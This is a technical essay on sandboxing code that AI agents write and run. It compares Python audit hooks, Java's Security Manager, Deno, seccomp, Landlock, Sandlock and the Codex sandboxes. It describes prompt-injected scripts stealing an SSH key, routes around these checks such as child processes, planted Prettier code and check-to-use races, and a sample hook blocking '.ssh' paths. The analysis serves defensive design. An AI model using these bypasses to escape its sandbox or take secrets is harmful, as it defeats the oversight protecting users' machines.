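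The proposal suggests events for these operations, among others:

| Operation | What the hook receives |
|---|---|
| Opening a file | The path, the mode and flags |
| Importing a module | The module's name and, where available, its file and the search paths |
| Compiling a string into code | The code and a file name, if there is one |
| Connecting a socket or looking up a host | The socket and the address |
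| Requesting a web address with `urllib` | The address, data, headers and method |
| Loading a native library with `ctypes` | The library's name or path |
| Changing an attribute of a type | The object, the attribute and the new value |

Event names and coverage vary with the Python version. The `urllib` event includes the data before encryption, so a hook, unlike Deno's broker, could check that the sales script sends only a number.

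To stop an operation, the hook raises an exception. A host could run this before the analyst's script:

```python
import sys

def check(event, args):
    if event == "open" and "/.ssh/" in str(args[0]):
        raise PermissionError("login keys are off limits")
    if event == "urllib.Request" and args[0] != REPORTING_API:
        raise PermissionError("address not approved")

sys.addaudithook(check)
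```

When the script tries to open the private key, CPython first calls `check` with the path. `check` raises an exception, so CPython does not open the file. Dower recommends that the program normally end at this point, although a hook may also just record the event or shut the process down at once. If the program continues, the script can catch the exception and try to get the key another way.

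The script could still get around this hook by changing its working directory to `.ssh` and opening the key by its bare name, or by sending data through a socket without using `urllib`. A stricter hook might permit only `sales.csv`, but then `import csv` would fail, because Python has to open the module's file to import it. The hook has to distinguish files that the interpreter needs from files that the script itself tries to open, but both produce the same kind of event.

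Dower says audit hooks are not a sandbox mainly because Python needs, for its normal work, the same functions that a sandbox has to remove. The many earlier attempts to sandbox CPython all failed for this reason. For instance, removing the ability to compile strings would break importing modules from source, but leaving any of it in place gives an attacker indirect ways to reach it. Dower also argues that detecting intruders matters more than stopping them early, since an early refusal drives them towards methods that are harder to notice. That is sensible for a company watching its own servers, but a code-execution tool expects hostile scripts from the start and needs to prevent the theft of a key, since recording the theft doesn't undo it.

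A program can't remove or replace a hook once it is installed. Dower also put the functions in Python's built-in `sys` module, because an attacker could have replaced a separate audit module with a dummy by adding a single line to a start-up file. But a hook written in Python reads its rules from memory that the script can reach, so the script in the example might change `REPORTING_API` without touching `check`. A hook written in C and installed before Python starts is harder to subvert. It also covers every interpreter in the process, while a hook added from Python covers only the interpreter that added it.

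Hermetic, an open-source tool that places guards inside Python programs, can block network access, child processes and native code. Without its `--seal` option, an agent could call the function that removes the guards. Hermetic's *AI Policy* advises developers to run a hostile agent inside a container or virtual machine even when the seal is on, and describes operating-system isolation as the actual security boundary.

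### Rewriting a program or evaluating it piece by piece

A host can also change the program before CPython runs it. RestrictedPython, a library from the developers of the Zope web server, parses a script into a syntax tree, rejects some constructs and replaces others with calls to host-supplied functions. The expression `row["amount"]` becomes a call to `_getitem_`, and `json.dumps` becomes a call to `_getattr_` with the attribute name `dumps`. The host also chooses which built-in functions the script can use. If it leaves out `open`, the line that reads the private key fails with a `NameError`.

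Attribute access needs checking because code can use it to get from one Python object to another. A function written in Python, for example, holds a reference to its module's global variables, which may include `os`, the module for working with files and processes. RestrictedPython therefore refuses attribute names that begin with an underscore, which covers most of Python's internal links. The rewritten program is still ordinary CPython code handling ordinary objects, so the rewriting misses any path between objects that doesn't appear as an attribute in the source. String formatting was one such path, because a format template can name an attribute, which Python then looks up inside its own library. The maintainers fixed that flaw in 2023, but they do not present RestrictedPython as a complete sandbox.

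The local executor in smolagents, Hugging Face's library for agents that act by writing Python, walks through the program's syntax tree and carries out each operation itself instead of handing the whole program to CPython. This method is called *restricted evaluation*. The executor blocks imports of modules that the developer hasn't authorised and limits the number of operations to stop endless loops.

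Hugging Face's local executor resembles Monty, but its values are real CPython objects, and an authorised function runs at full speed with the host process's access. If a developer authorises an image library, a script can use it to fill the disk with pictures, even though the executor provides no way to write files. Hugging Face does not consider the executor a security boundary and supports containers and remote sandboxes for untrusted code. The executor is more useful for catching a model's mistakes, such as importing a module the task doesn't need.

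### Java's Security Manager

Java's designers put hooks throughout the standard library to guard against a threat much like that of model-written scripts. Web browsers used to download small Java programs called applets and run them on the user's machine. From Java 1.0, library code called a component named the Security Manager to check permissions before opening a file or connection. According to OpenJDK's *JEP 411* (2021), these checks were feasible because the library then had only eight packages. The checks kept applets from reaching the user's files or the network and left local code unrestricted.

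As the library quickly grew, trusted code could do more damage. Java 1.2 therefore treated all code as untrusted by default and let users grant permissions to each body of code separately. This raises a problem when one piece of code calls another. Suppose the sales script were a Java program that could read only sales.csv, but it used a CSV library that could read all the analyst's files. If the Security Manager checked only the CSV library's permissions, the script could pass the library the path of the private key and get the contents back.

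The Security Manager instead used *stack inspection*. The call stack lists the functions that are still running, each of which called the next. When the CSV library tries to open the key, the stack holds the script, the library and Java's own file code. Java allowed the operation only if all the code on the stack had permission, so the script's lack of permission was enough for Java to refuse it.

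A library sometimes has to do things its caller isn't permitted to do. For example, a script without permission to read files can still request the time in another city, which requires Java to read its own time-zone file. The library can have the Security Manager check the library's own permissions and ignore those of its callers. This is safe only if the caller can't choose which file is read, and the library's developer has to ensure that everywhere the library makes this exception.

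In *JEP 486*, Mullan and Buckley (2024) count over 1,000 methods in Java's library that had to check permissions and over 1,200 that had to raise their own permissions. The maintainers had to review every change to these methods and design every new feature with the Security Manager in mind. Yet Java left the Security Manager off by default, and few applications turned it on.

OpenJDK gives several reasons for this disuse. A developer who wanted to restrict only file reading also had to find and grant every other permission that her program used. Stack inspection made this worse because an application needed the permissions of the libraries it called, even if its own code didn't use them, so many developers granted every permission. The checks were also slow, and the Security Manager could not address 19 of the 25 weaknesses on a 2020 industry list of the most dangerous kinds of software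 weakness. Java had also dropped support for applets, the original reason for the mechanism.

OpenJDK deprecated the Security Manager in Java 17, and programs that enabled it began printing warnings. Mullan and Buckley found hardly any public discussion of those warnings, which they took as a sign that few developers cared. Java 24 permanently disabled the Security Manager, and the runtime now won't start if someone tries to turn it on. The maintainers plan to remove its programming interface later. They expected to delete over 50,000 lines of code, including tests.

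Some of these reasons don't apply to a code-execution tool. A script written by a model under an attacker's influence is closer to an applet than to a company's server program, so the threat that receded for Java remains here. Such a script also needs only a few permissions, which the host can list. But the maintenance burden still applies. If a thousand methods must each call the check, any method that omits it is unprotected. Deno's flaw in reading a file's status was such an omission.

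Java's maintainers advise sandboxing Java programs from outside, with containers, virtual machines or operating system controls. For the few who only want to intercept a call, Mullan and Buckley show how to rewrite compiled Java code as it loads. Their example replaces every call to `System.exit`, which ends the program, with code that raises an error. This can stop a plug-in from accidentally shutting down its host application, but they warn that malicious code can get around such interception in countless ways.

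### Deno's work on per-module and per-function permissions

Stack inspection reappeared in Deno in 2026. The source code change *feat(permissions): add --deny-module for per-module permission restrictions* adds a flag that denies permissions to chosen modules. With `--deny-module=npm:lodash:net,run`, Deno would block network access and stop new processes from starting whenever lodash is anywhere on the call stack, whatever the program's other flags allow. Developers would name only the modules they distrust, which would avoid Java's long lists of grants. But the stack shows only code that is still running, so a denied library could return an attacker's address to the main program, which would then contact that address with its own permissions.

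The flag would also be a poor fit for a code-execution tool. The script is the untrusted code in such a tool, and a developer might want to deny it network access while letting it call a trusted `send_total` module. Under the rule in the change, the script would still be on the stack when that module tried to connect, so Deno would refuse the connection. Java let trusted code use its own permissions regardless of its caller's, but the description of Deno's flag doesn't include an equivalent.

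The Deno change *feat(permissions): prototype per-API (capability) permissions* gives individual functions their own permissions. For example, a developer could allow `fetch` to reach certain hosts but forbid the script to open a raw connection to them. The prototype covers only network calls, takes its settings from an environment variable, and adds its check to Deno's existing permission checks.

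Neither feature appears to have shipped. Deno's permissions reference from May 2026 lists neither, and its security guide from June still states that modules on one thread can't have different privileges. These documents may be older than the code changes, so they aren't conclusive. Cloudflare's announcement in October that it was acquiring Deno is a stronger reason to doubt a release. Willison (2026), in *Deno is joining Cloudflare*, quotes the team's plan to publish bug fixes and security updates for another year and then stop developing the runtime. Deno remains open source, so others may continue the work.

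Node.js, the more widely used JavaScript runtime, has had a stable permission system since January 2025. When Willison wrote, it could still only allow or block all network access, so it couldn't confine the sales script to the reporting service.

### Native libraries and child processes

All these checks depend on the script reaching the outside world through the runtime. A *native library* contains compiled machine code, which can make system calls directly. Deno can check the call that loads the library, but it can't intervene once the library is running. The library can then read the private key even if the script has no permission to read any file. Python's audit hooks have the same limit. They can report or block an attempt to load a library through `ctypes`, but the system calls that the library makes afterwards don't trigger them. In *PEP 578*, Heimes (2019), who had the final decision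 on the proposal, accepted that Python couldn't provide a fully secure hook for native code.

Forbidding all native code in CPython would also block NumPy and pandas, which contain it. A host can instead permit the installed copies and refuse libraries from any directory where the script may write, so that the script can't create and load a library of its own. The permitted packages then become part of the trusted computing base, since a memory error in one of them could let the script run machine code.

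Child processes also bypass Deno's checks, just as `curl` bypassed the hook on `urlopen`. If the developer lets the sales script start `curl`, the broker receives one request to run it, and `curl` can then read the private key and upload it without contacting the broker again. Permission to start Deno itself is just as dangerous, because the script can start a second copy with all permissions. Even a harmless program becomes a risk if the script may write to its directory, because the script can replace the program with one of its own and run that under the approved name.

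Deno therefore tells developers to treat permission to run programs or load native libraries as equivalent to full access. For untrusted code, it recommends combining minimal permissions, a separate worker thread with fewer permissions than the main program, the operating system's sandboxing features, and a virtual machine or similar environment.

*I was a fan of Deno's security model* (MacWright, 2026) describes four years at Val Town, which runs its users' JavaScript. The company first used vm2, a sandboxing library that proved inadequate, and then moved to Deno. It disabled prompts, supplied an artificial set of environment variables, and avoided the child-process gap by never giving users' code permission to start other programs. MacWright reports no security failure in which Deno's flags were at fault. This is one company's experience and covers only failures that someone noticed, but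 the code did come from strangers.

Val Town repeatedly considered adding Linux's own isolation features, but its hosting provider, like most, ran customers' programs in Docker containers without the privileges those features required. To use them, Val Town would have had to manage its own servers. Deno's permission flags worked on both the hosted machines and developers' laptops. On a machine the developer controls, the kernel can restrict native libraries and child processes as well as the script.

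## How does the operating system intercept privileged calls?

If the sales script starts `curl`, `curl` still needs a system call to the kernel to open a socket, so a hook on system calls also catches what Deno's and Python's checks miss.

Researchers at the University of California, Berkeley, built an early tool of this kind, Janus, in 1996. At the time, web browsers passed many downloaded documents to separate viewers, and a malicious document could exploit a bug to take over the viewer. Janus used a debugging facility in the Solaris operating system that stops a process whenever it makes a chosen system call. While the viewer was stopped, Janus read the call's arguments, compared them with a policy file, and either let the call continue or made it fail.

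Switching to another process for every check is slow. Systrace, which Niels Provos presented in 2003, therefore kept part of the policy in the kernel. The kernel directly handled calls that the policy always allowed or always refused. It passed only the others to a separate program, such as calls to open a file, where the decision depends on the path. Systrace could also draft a policy by recording what a program did during a normal run. Linux now has several mechanisms that divide the checks in different ways.

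### What each Linux mechanism receives

Seccomp entered Linux in 2005. In its original mode, a process gives up all system calls except reading and writing files it already has open, returning from a signal handler, and exiting. This is enough for a pure calculation but not for Python, which opens many files just to start.

A later version lets a developer supply a *seccomp filter*, a small program that the kernel runs at each system call. The filter receives the call's number and its arguments. When the sales script connects to the reporting service on an ordinary Intel or AMD machine, it gets something like this:

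```text
call number   42                connect
argument 1    5                 the script's handle for the socket
argument 2    0x7ffc3a1e8b40    where the destination is in memory
argument 3    16                the length of the destination in bytes
```

The filter can't look up what is stored at `0x7ffc3a1e8b40`, so it can't distinguish the reporting service from the attacker's server. It can refuse every `connect`, or refuse to create internet sockets at all, because the socket type is passed as a plain number. File paths are also in memory, so a filter can't distinguish sales.csv from the private key. A process can't remove its filter, and its child processes inherit the filter. Filters also miss operations that a program submits through io_uring, a Linux feature for queuing file and network requests in shared memory, so a sandbox that relies on filters usually blocks io_uring too.

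With *seccomp user notification*, a filter can refer a system call to a supervisor, a trusted process outside the sandbox. The kernel suspends the calling thread and sends the supervisor the same numbers the filter received. The supervisor can then read the destination or path from the script's memory, apply any policy, and either return an error or a result or tell the kernel to continue the original call. This resembles Janus, but the filter determines which calls go to the supervisor.

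*Landlock* works further inside the kernel. A process lists the files and directories it will need, and the kernel blocks any other access of the kinds the list covers. The kernel follows any `..` or symbolic link before it checks the file, so the script can't get around the rules by spelling the private key's path differently. Applying Landlock doesn't require administrator rights, and the process can't undo it. But its network rules cover only port numbers, so a rule that allows port 443, the standard port for encrypted web traffic, also allows connections to the attacker's server on that port.

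Landlock runs its checks at *security-module hooks*, fixed points in the kernel's code just before a sensitive operation. By then, the kernel has already found the file or copied the network address out of the program's memory. Developers can attach their own checks to these hooks with eBPF, a system for loading small programs into the kernel after it verifies that they are safe to run. An eBPF program can keep counts between calls, so it could refuse a script's eleventh connection. However, it must decide immediately and can't wait for a person to respond. Loading one generally requires administrator rights, which suits a company running its own servers better than a developer on a managed laptop.

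Google's *gVisor* puts a second kernel between the script and Linux. This kernel is an ordinary program that receives all the script's system calls and carries them out itself, making a much smaller set of calls to the real kernel. As a result, the script usually can't reach a flaw in how Linux handles a rare call. However, system calls are slower, and programs that depend on details gVisor handles differently occasionally fail.

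| Mechanism | What it receives when the script opens sales.csv | What it can do |
|---|---|---|
| Seccomp filter | The call's number and the memory address of the path | Allow or refuse the call, end the process, or refer the call to a supervisor |
| User notification | The same, with the script paused so that the supervisor can read the path | Anything the developer can program, including performing the call |
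| Landlock | The file that the kernel has found | Allow or refuse, according to a list |
| eBPF security hook | The file that the kernel has found | Allow or refuse, according to a program that can keep counts |
| gVisor | The complete call | Carry it out or refuse it, without passing it to Linux |

### How Sandlock divides the work

None of these mechanisms alone suits the sales script. Landlock can protect the private key but can't limit the script to one server. A supervisor can do both but would slow down every file access. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes an open-source tool that combines Landlock, seccomp filters and user notification. The tool runs on a developer's own Linux machine without administrator rights.

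Sandlock puts a rule in the kernel if it can determine before the program starts whether to allow a call. For the sales script, a Landlock rule would let the script read sales.csv and Python's own files but nothing else in the analyst's home directory. A seccomp filter refuses dangerous calls that Landlock doesn't cover. Sandlock sends a call to the supervisor only if the decision depends on a run-time value, such as a network destination. If neither the kernel nor the supervisor can decide reliably, Sandlock refuses the call.

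To start a command, Sandlock creates a child process, which applies the Landlock rules and the filter to itself. The child then waits until the supervisor is ready to receive notifications before loading the script. Sandlock needs Linux 6.12 or later for the Landlock features it uses, and it won't fall back to weaker protection on an older kernel.

GitLab, a platform for hosting and testing code, does the opposite by default for its agents. *How to verify your GitLab Duo Agent Platform sandbox rules* explains that the sandbox needs permission to create namespaces, which give a process its own view of resources such as the file system. If the sandbox can't start, the agent's job runs without protection, with a warning in the log. Since version 19.6, an administrator can make such jobs fail instead. But GitLab detects the sandbox by looking for its program file in the job, so a project that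 supplies its own container image could include a different program under that name.

### One connect call through the supervisor

Suppose the host permits the sales script to contact only `reports.example.com` on port 443:

1. When the sandbox starts, Sandlock looks up the name once and stores the IP address, say 203.0.113.10.
2. The script runs `urlopen`, which creates a socket and calls `connect`. The seccomp filter refers the call to the supervisor, and the kernel suspends the script.
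3. The supervisor copies the destination from the script's memory into its own and confirms that the suspended call is still waiting.
4. It compares the copy with the stored address and port. If they differ, it returns an error, which Python raises as an exception.
5. If they match, the supervisor obtains a duplicate of the script's socket and calls `connect` on it with its own copy of the destination.
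6. The supervisor returns the result. Both handles refer to the same socket, so the script's socket is now connected and the script continues as if it had made the call.

The kernel never carries out the script's original `connect`, so the script gains nothing by changing the destination after the check.

Landlock blocks the attacker's attempt to open the private key, and the supervisor isn't involved. If the script still tries to contact the attacker's server, the supervisor blocks the connection at step 4. But step 4 compares IP addresses, and hosting companies often serve many customers from one address, so an attacker with an account at the same company as an allowed site might still receive data. (Sandlock has optional rules on web requests for such cases.) Sandlock also can't accept a rule for every subdomain of a company, because it stores addresses and would have no complete list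 of names to look up.

The supervisor also counts new processes and refuses any beyond a limit. It adds up the memory that the script requests and ends the script if the total is too high. Wang and Zheng consider these limits adequate for buggy code, but they recommend the kernel's resource controls against deliberate attempts to exhaust memory, because some kinds of memory growth bypass the calls that Sandlock intercepts.

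Sandlock can also capture changes to files. When a script writes to a project, the supervisor redirects the write to a separate directory, and the script's later reads return the changed version. After the script ends, the host can merge the changes, discard them, or keep them for inspection. If a script deleted the analyst's spreadsheets, they would disappear only from the script's view until someone accepted the deletion. Sandlock has no equivalent for network traffic, because a total that has reached the reporting service can't be recalled.

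### The policy callback

A developer can also give Sandlock a function to run when the script makes selected system calls, including those that start a program, open a file or make a connection. The script waits until the function returns. The function can allow the call, refuse it with a chosen error, or allow it and flag it for later review. It can also tighten the policy for the rest of the run.

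Suppose the model submits one shell command that installs a plotting package and then runs `chart.py`, which draws the sales figures. The installation needs the network, and the chart doesn't. In the style of Wang and Zheng's example, the callback could be:

```python
def on_event(event, ctx):
    if event.syscall == "execve" and event.argv_contains("chart.py"):
        ctx.restrict_network([])              # installation is over
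        ctx.deny_path("/home/analyst/.ssh")
        return "audit"                        # allow, but flag it
    return 0                                  # allow
```

`execve` is the system call that loads a new program, and `argv` is the list of words in the command. When the shell starts Python with `chart.py`, Sandlock pauses the `execve` call and runs the callback, which removes network access before the script runs.

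The callback receives the command's words but not file paths, which Sandlock leaves to Landlock. It therefore can't allow or refuse files by name.

Wang and Zheng warn that matching words in a command is only a signal, because a hostile program can use another name. The callback removes access when it recognises a name, so a model under the attacker's influence could keep the network on by saving the same code as `plot.py`. The host could avoid this by running the installation and the chart as separate commands, each with its own fixed rules. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the cloud version of its coding agent, Codex, similarly separates setup from the agent's phase. Setup has network access and any secrets it needs. OpenAI's system then removes the secrets and, by default, the network before the agent's phase starts. The callback is more useful when the host knows something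 that the fixed rules couldn't include, such as whether this task should start other programs.

### Ten checks and the cost of a round trip

Wang and Zheng tested Sandlock on a workstation with a six-core AMD Ryzen 5 5500U, 8 GB of memory and Linux 6.18. They first ran ten pass-or-fail checks, and Sandlock passed them all. For example, a program could read a file inside its permitted directories but not one outside them, and could connect to a listed server but not an unlisted one. A program limited to four processes could not start more. The checks confirm that the rules take effect in ordinary use, but they don't include attempts to break the sandbox, and nobody knows how Sandlock would do in a contest like Monty's.

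Running `/bin/echo`, which only prints its arguments, took about 6 milliseconds under Sandlock, of which about 5 were overhead. Docker took roughly 44 times as long. A model may run dozens of short commands a minute, so using Sandlock instead of Docker saves perhaps ten seconds per minute.

The throughput test used Redis, a database that keeps its data in memory, with 100,000 requests from 50 simultaneous clients. Redis handled about 75,200 writes per second under Sandlock and 75,500 without it, and reads were slightly faster under Sandlock, so the differences are within measurement noise. Under Docker, Redis ran at about 76 percent of the unsandboxed rate. The test used Sandlock's default fixed rules, which leave nearly all of Redis's calls to the kernel, so it doesn't measure how much the supervisor slows a program.

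In a separate test, two sandboxed programs exchanged 256-byte messages, and the supervisor handled every send. The median round trip rose from 20 to 55 microseconds, while Docker added nothing. The slowest one percent took at least 114 microseconds, up from 33. Wang and Zheng call the delay immaterial for agents because a request to a language model takes between a tenth of a second and ten seconds. That is right for the sales script, which would need almost 3,000 such exchanges to add a tenth of a second, but a script that sends a database many small queries would slow down noticeably. The evaluation doesn't time the file operations that the supervisor also handles when it captures changes.

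Ordinary `python3`, `node`, `make` and `pytest` ran in Sandlock once they had access to their temporary directories, and Python could import packages with compiled code. Packages such as NumPy, which Monty can't run, should therefore work, although Wang and Zheng leave systematic testing to later work. Sandlock also needs no special privileges, which might have helped Val Town if its hosting provider's kernel was recent enough.

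### What Codex permits by default

OpenAI's Codex also runs on developers' own computers, and it has to work on macOS and Windows as well as Linux. According to OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* (November 2026), commands may by default write inside the project's directory and read most files the user can read, but they may not use the network.

Some directories inside the project remain read-only, including `.codex`, which holds Codex's settings, and `.git`, which can hold scripts that Git runs automatically. A script with write access to the settings could loosen the rules for the next command, much as Pirch and colleagues did with IronClaw.

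The read permission is much broader than Sandlock's. The script could still read the analyst's private key and any settings file containing an access key. OpenAI accepts this because compilers and other tools depend on files all over the machine, and many would break if reads were limited to the project. With the network off, the script can't send the key anywhere directly, but it can print the key into the text that the model reads, and a tool outside the sandbox could then pass it on.

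Users can choose stricter rules. OpenAI's documentation of permission profiles, a feature still in beta, includes a ready-made list, `:minimal`, of the system files that common tools need. *Improving a Coding Agent Harness* had given up on compiling such a list for Python. For the sales task, a profile might be:

```toml
default_permissions = "sales"

[permissions.sales.filesystem]
":minimal" = "read"

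[permissions.sales.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"." = "read"

[permissions.sales.network]
enabled = true

[permissions.sales.network.domains]
"reports.example.com" = "allow"
```

The script can now read the project and the system files, neither of which contains the private key. A user who prefers the broad default can instead add a rule that denies `~/.ssh`. Rules can also deny a pattern, such as all files ending in `.env`, where developers often keep access keys. On Linux and Windows, Codex lists the files that match a pattern before the sandbox starts, so a file that appears later may not be included.

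OpenAI describes an attack that the default rules permit. Many JavaScript projects keep a copy of Prettier, a code formatter, in a subdirectory that Git ignores. The agent is allowed to write there, so it can insert malicious code into Prettier. If the user's editor runs Prettier whenever she saves a file, the code then runs outside the sandbox with all her permissions. No system call in the attack breaks the rules, because the write stays inside the project and the editor was never in the sandbox. OpenAI relies partly on the model's training to prevent this, which is weak protection if an attacker can deceive the model, as Pirch and colleagues assume.

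### Enforcing the rules on macOS, Linux and Windows

On macOS, Codex uses Seatbelt, the system's built-in sandbox, which OpenAI says needs no setup. Codex writes a file of rules for the command it is about to run, and the kernel applies them to that command and all its descendants. Codex can change the rules for the next command by writing a different file.

According to *Inside the Codex Windows Sandbox* (Vaughan, 2026), Codex on Linux combines Landlock and a seccomp filter with bubblewrap, a program that starts a command in its own namespaces. Bubblewrap can make a directory read-only inside those namespaces or leave it out. If it leaves out the analyst's `.ssh` directory, the script can't open the key because the file doesn't exist inside the namespaces.

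Windows had nothing equivalent that suited a coding agent, so Wiesen and his colleagues at OpenAI built a sandbox from other parts of the system, as he explains in *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*. They rejected AppContainer, the Windows application sandbox, because it suits only programs whose needs are known in advance. Windows Sandbox, a disposable virtual machine, would have separated Codex from the user's actual files and tools, and home editions of Windows don't include it.

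Codex limits writing on Windows with a *write-restricted token*. Windows gives each process a token that identifies its user, and each file has a list of who may do what with it. With a write-restricted token, a write succeeds only if both the user and at least one identity on a separate list in the token have permission. Codex creates an artificial identity for the sandbox, puts it on that list, and grants it write access to the project but not to `.git` or `.codex`. A sandboxed command can't change the user's other documents, even though the user can, because the artificial identity lacks write access to them.

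Network access was harder to restrict. The first version set environment variables that directed web traffic to a dead address, and it put dummy versions of some network programs where the shell would find them first. A program that ignored the variables and opened its own socket could still connect. Wiesen calls these measures "advisory" and says they would not have withstood hostile code. Windows Firewall could block the connection, but it couldn't apply a rule to the artificial identity. A rule for the analyst's account would have cut off her browser, and a rule for `python.exe` would have affected all her Python programs.

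The current version therefore creates two extra Windows users, one with network access and one that the firewall blocks, and runs each sandboxed command as one of them. Setup requires an administrator's approval. The design also needs a small helper program, because Codex runs as the analyst and couldn't reliably start a restricted process for another user.

One Windows user normally can't read another's personal directory, so separate users alone would have protected some of the analyst's files. But Codex is supposed to be able to read whatever she can, so the setup grants the new users access to her directory.

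### When the kernel itself is the weak point

Sandlock and the local versions of Codex run the script on the machine's own kernel. They can refuse many system calls, but Python needs many others, which the kernel carries out with full control of the machine. A script that exploits a memory error in the kernel code handling those calls can switch off Landlock, the system-call filter and the sandbox's other restrictions. Wang and Zheng exclude kernel flaws from the attacks Sandlock is meant to stop. They also exclude side channels, in which a program infers secrets from effects such as timing, and deliberate exhaustion of the kernel's shared resources.

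A virtual machine gives the script its own kernel. The script's system calls go to this guest kernel, which reaches the real machine only through a few virtual devices, such as a disk and a network card. An attacker who breaks the guest kernel controls the virtual machine but still needs a second flaw, in the software or hardware that isolates it, to reach the host. gVisor offers some of this protection without a full virtual machine, because the script must break gVisor's kernel before it can attack Linux through the few calls gVisor makes.

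Wang and Zheng recommend a *microVM*, a stripped-down virtual machine that starts quickly, when mutually hostile customers share a computer. Otherwise, one customer's kernel exploit would expose everyone else's data. They give a start-up time of about 100 milliseconds for the microVM Firecracker, although their benchmarks time only Docker and Sandlock. On one developer's laptop, where the most likely problems are a model's mistakes and planted instructions to retrieve a readable file, kernel hooks stop most of the damage with much less overhead. That reasoning weakens if the laptop holds something valuable enough to justify a kernel exploit, since planted instructions could also lead the model to download and run one.

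Virtual machines are becoming easier to use for this purpose. *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) presents three prototypes in which the agent stays on the user's Mac but sends its commands to a separate Linux system. One runs Linux in an emulator compiled to WebAssembly and needs only Node.js. The others use Apple's container software and QEMU, an established program for running virtual machines. The Linux system can access only the folders the user chooses and has no network access by default. Keeping the agent outside the Linux system also prevents its commands from altering the agent.

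A virtual machine doesn't inspect individual calls, however. If the user shares her project folder with write access, a command in the virtual machine can plant code in Prettier, as a command in Codex's sandbox can, and her editor will run that code on the Mac. Sharing the folder as read-only prevents this, but then the agent can't edit the project.

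## Is the call that was checked the call that runs?

A system call's arguments can change while a supervisor inspects them. Suppose a supervisor simpler than Sandlock's reads the destination of a `connect` call, finds it on the approved list, and tells the kernel to continue the call. The kernel has paused the thread that made the call, but a script can run several threads, which all share the same memory.

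| Step | What happens | Address in the script's memory |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | One thread calls `connect`, and the kernel pauses it | The reporting service |
| 2 | The supervisor reads the address and approves the call | The reporting service |
| 3 | Another thread overwrites the address | The attacker's server |
| 4 | The kernel resumes the call, reads the address again and connects | The attacker's server |

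This is a *check-to-use race*, or TOCTOU ("time of check to time of use"). The policy was right and the hook ran, but it checked a different connection from the one the kernel made.

Only arguments stored in memory can change this way. The caller passes plain numbers in processor registers, which the kernel copies as soon as the call arrives. A seccomp filter receives only those numbers, so it avoids the race.

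### Five classes of error in Janus

Janus, the Berkeley sandbox from 1996, went through several rewrites, and its developers kept finding ways around their own checks. *Traps and Pitfalls* (Garfinkel, 2003) sorts the mistakes behind such bypasses into five classes. The paper still appears in MIT's lecture notes, *System call interposition* (2025).

The first class of mistake is duplicating the operating system's work. Janus needed to know which network protocol each socket used, so it recorded the protocol when a program created the socket and looked it up later. But Unix lets a program reassign a file descriptor to a different socket, after which Janus's record was wrong. Experienced Unix programmers wrote this code and several other people read it, yet nobody noticed the mistake until a rewrite several years later. The fix was to ask the kernel for the protocol each time.

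Developers also overlook indirect routes to a resource. A program that is not allowed to open files can still create one by crashing, if the system saves a crashed program's memory to disk. It can also receive an open file from another process, or get a helper service to look something up for it.

The third class is race conditions, and the fourth is permitting only part of a complicated interface without understanding how its parts interact. Garfinkel's example is a series of failed attempts to make symbolic links safe. If the sandbox forbids a program to create links to protected files, the program can still use links that already exist. If the sandbox also forbids creating or renaming any link, the program can still rename a directory that contains one. Refusing to open a file that is itself a link doesn't help when a directory earlier in the path is a link. Garfinkel concluded that forbidding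 operations alone didn't seem to offer a general solution.

The last class is damage caused by refusing calls. Some programs start with administrator rights and then make a system call to give them up. If a sandbox refuses that call, a program that ignores the error keeps running with those rights. Garfinkel found this flaw in several common FreeBSD services after a casual look.

### Races over files and shared state

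The race in the opening table is an *argument race*. File names allow other races, even if nobody changes the script's memory. A supervisor might follow a symbolic link, find that it leads to sales.csv, and approve the call. If another process then redirects the link, the kernel opens the private key. A path containing `..` has a similar weakness, because it depends on where the current directory is, and another process may move that directory.

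Many tools try to prevent this by resolving the file's full path, without links or `..`, before they check it. Garfinkel explains that this only reduces the number of possible changes. Another process can still replace any directory in the path with a link before the kernel uses it. Hard links cause a separate problem for rules based on file names. A hard link is a second ordinary name for the same file, so resolving the path doesn't reveal the other name.

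Threads also share their current directory and their table of open handles. One thread can therefore change the directory after the supervisor has approved another thread's request to open `totals.csv`, or make handle 7 refer to a different socket.

Janus solved the argument race by copying paths and network addresses into the kernel's memory before checking them. This took about a quarter of the code in its kernel module. Copying didn't solve the races over shared directories and handles, so Janus didn't allow multithreaded programs. That would severely restrict a code-execution tool today, since many numerical libraries use threads.

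### Watson's attacks on system-call wrappers

In 2007 the security researcher Robert Watson showed that other tools had the same weakness. He summarised his results in *USENIX WOOT07, Exploiting Concurrency Vulnerabilities in System Call Wrappers* (2007), a post on the blog Light Blue Touchpaper. A *system-call wrapper* is code that runs around a system call to check or change it. Watson listed Systrace, two other wrapper systems and some commercial virus scanners among the affected products. He demonstrated working attacks on two sets of rules, one running on Systrace.

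The developers of these tools assumed that a system call happens in one indivisible step. Watson called it "trivial" to intervene between the check and the call, even on a single-processor computer, where threads take turns. The vendors had at least six months' notice of the problem, and some had known for years.

Watson concluded that wrappers are a bad idea unless one is willing to rebuild the operating system around message passing, in which a program sends its request as a separate message. He recommended checks built into the kernel instead, such as those at Linux's security-module hooks. Both approaches have since been used in sandboxes for model-written code.

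### The warning in the Linux manual

Seccomp user notification came later, and its manual page, Linux man-pages' *seccomp_unotify(2)*, repeats Watson's objection, warning that the mechanism "must not be used to make security policy decisions about the system call". In *seccomp_unotify.2*, the change that added the warning, Brauner, Cook and Kerrisk credit Jann Horn of Google with reporting the problem.

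The manual's reason is the race. After a supervisor tells the kernel to continue a call, the kernel reads the arguments from the program's memory again, and an attacker may have changed them. A supervisor should therefore continue a call only if the kernel or another security mechanism would block a harmful version anyway. The supervisor's intended role is to perform actions that the program lacks the privilege to perform itself, such as attaching a disk to a container.

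Sandlock is a security tool built on this mechanism, which seems to contradict the manual, but the race doesn't arise if the supervisor carries out the call itself and the kernel never resumes the original. Wang and Zheng regard this as the documented use. Their reading is reasonable for `connect`, where the supervisor either makes the connection or refuses it. It doesn't cover the calls that Sandlock lets the kernel continue, which need a different remedy.

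The manual also describes a race that affects a supervisor even when it only reads. A signal can interrupt the waiting program, which may then abandon the call and reuse the memory that held the path. The supervisor would then read the new contents as a path. After each read, it must therefore confirm that the call is still pending before it uses the result. For the same reason, according to the manual, a supervisor can never safely write to the program's memory.

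### Performing the call on the program's behalf

Garfinkel, Pfaff and Rosenblum (2004), in *Ostia*, rebuilt the sandbox so that the component that checks a request also carries it out. When a script opens a file in Ostia:

1. A small kernel module stops the call and redirects it to a library that Ostia has loaded into the script's memory.
2. The library sends the path to an *agent*, a trusted process outside the sandbox.
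3. The agent checks the path against the policy and opens the file itself.
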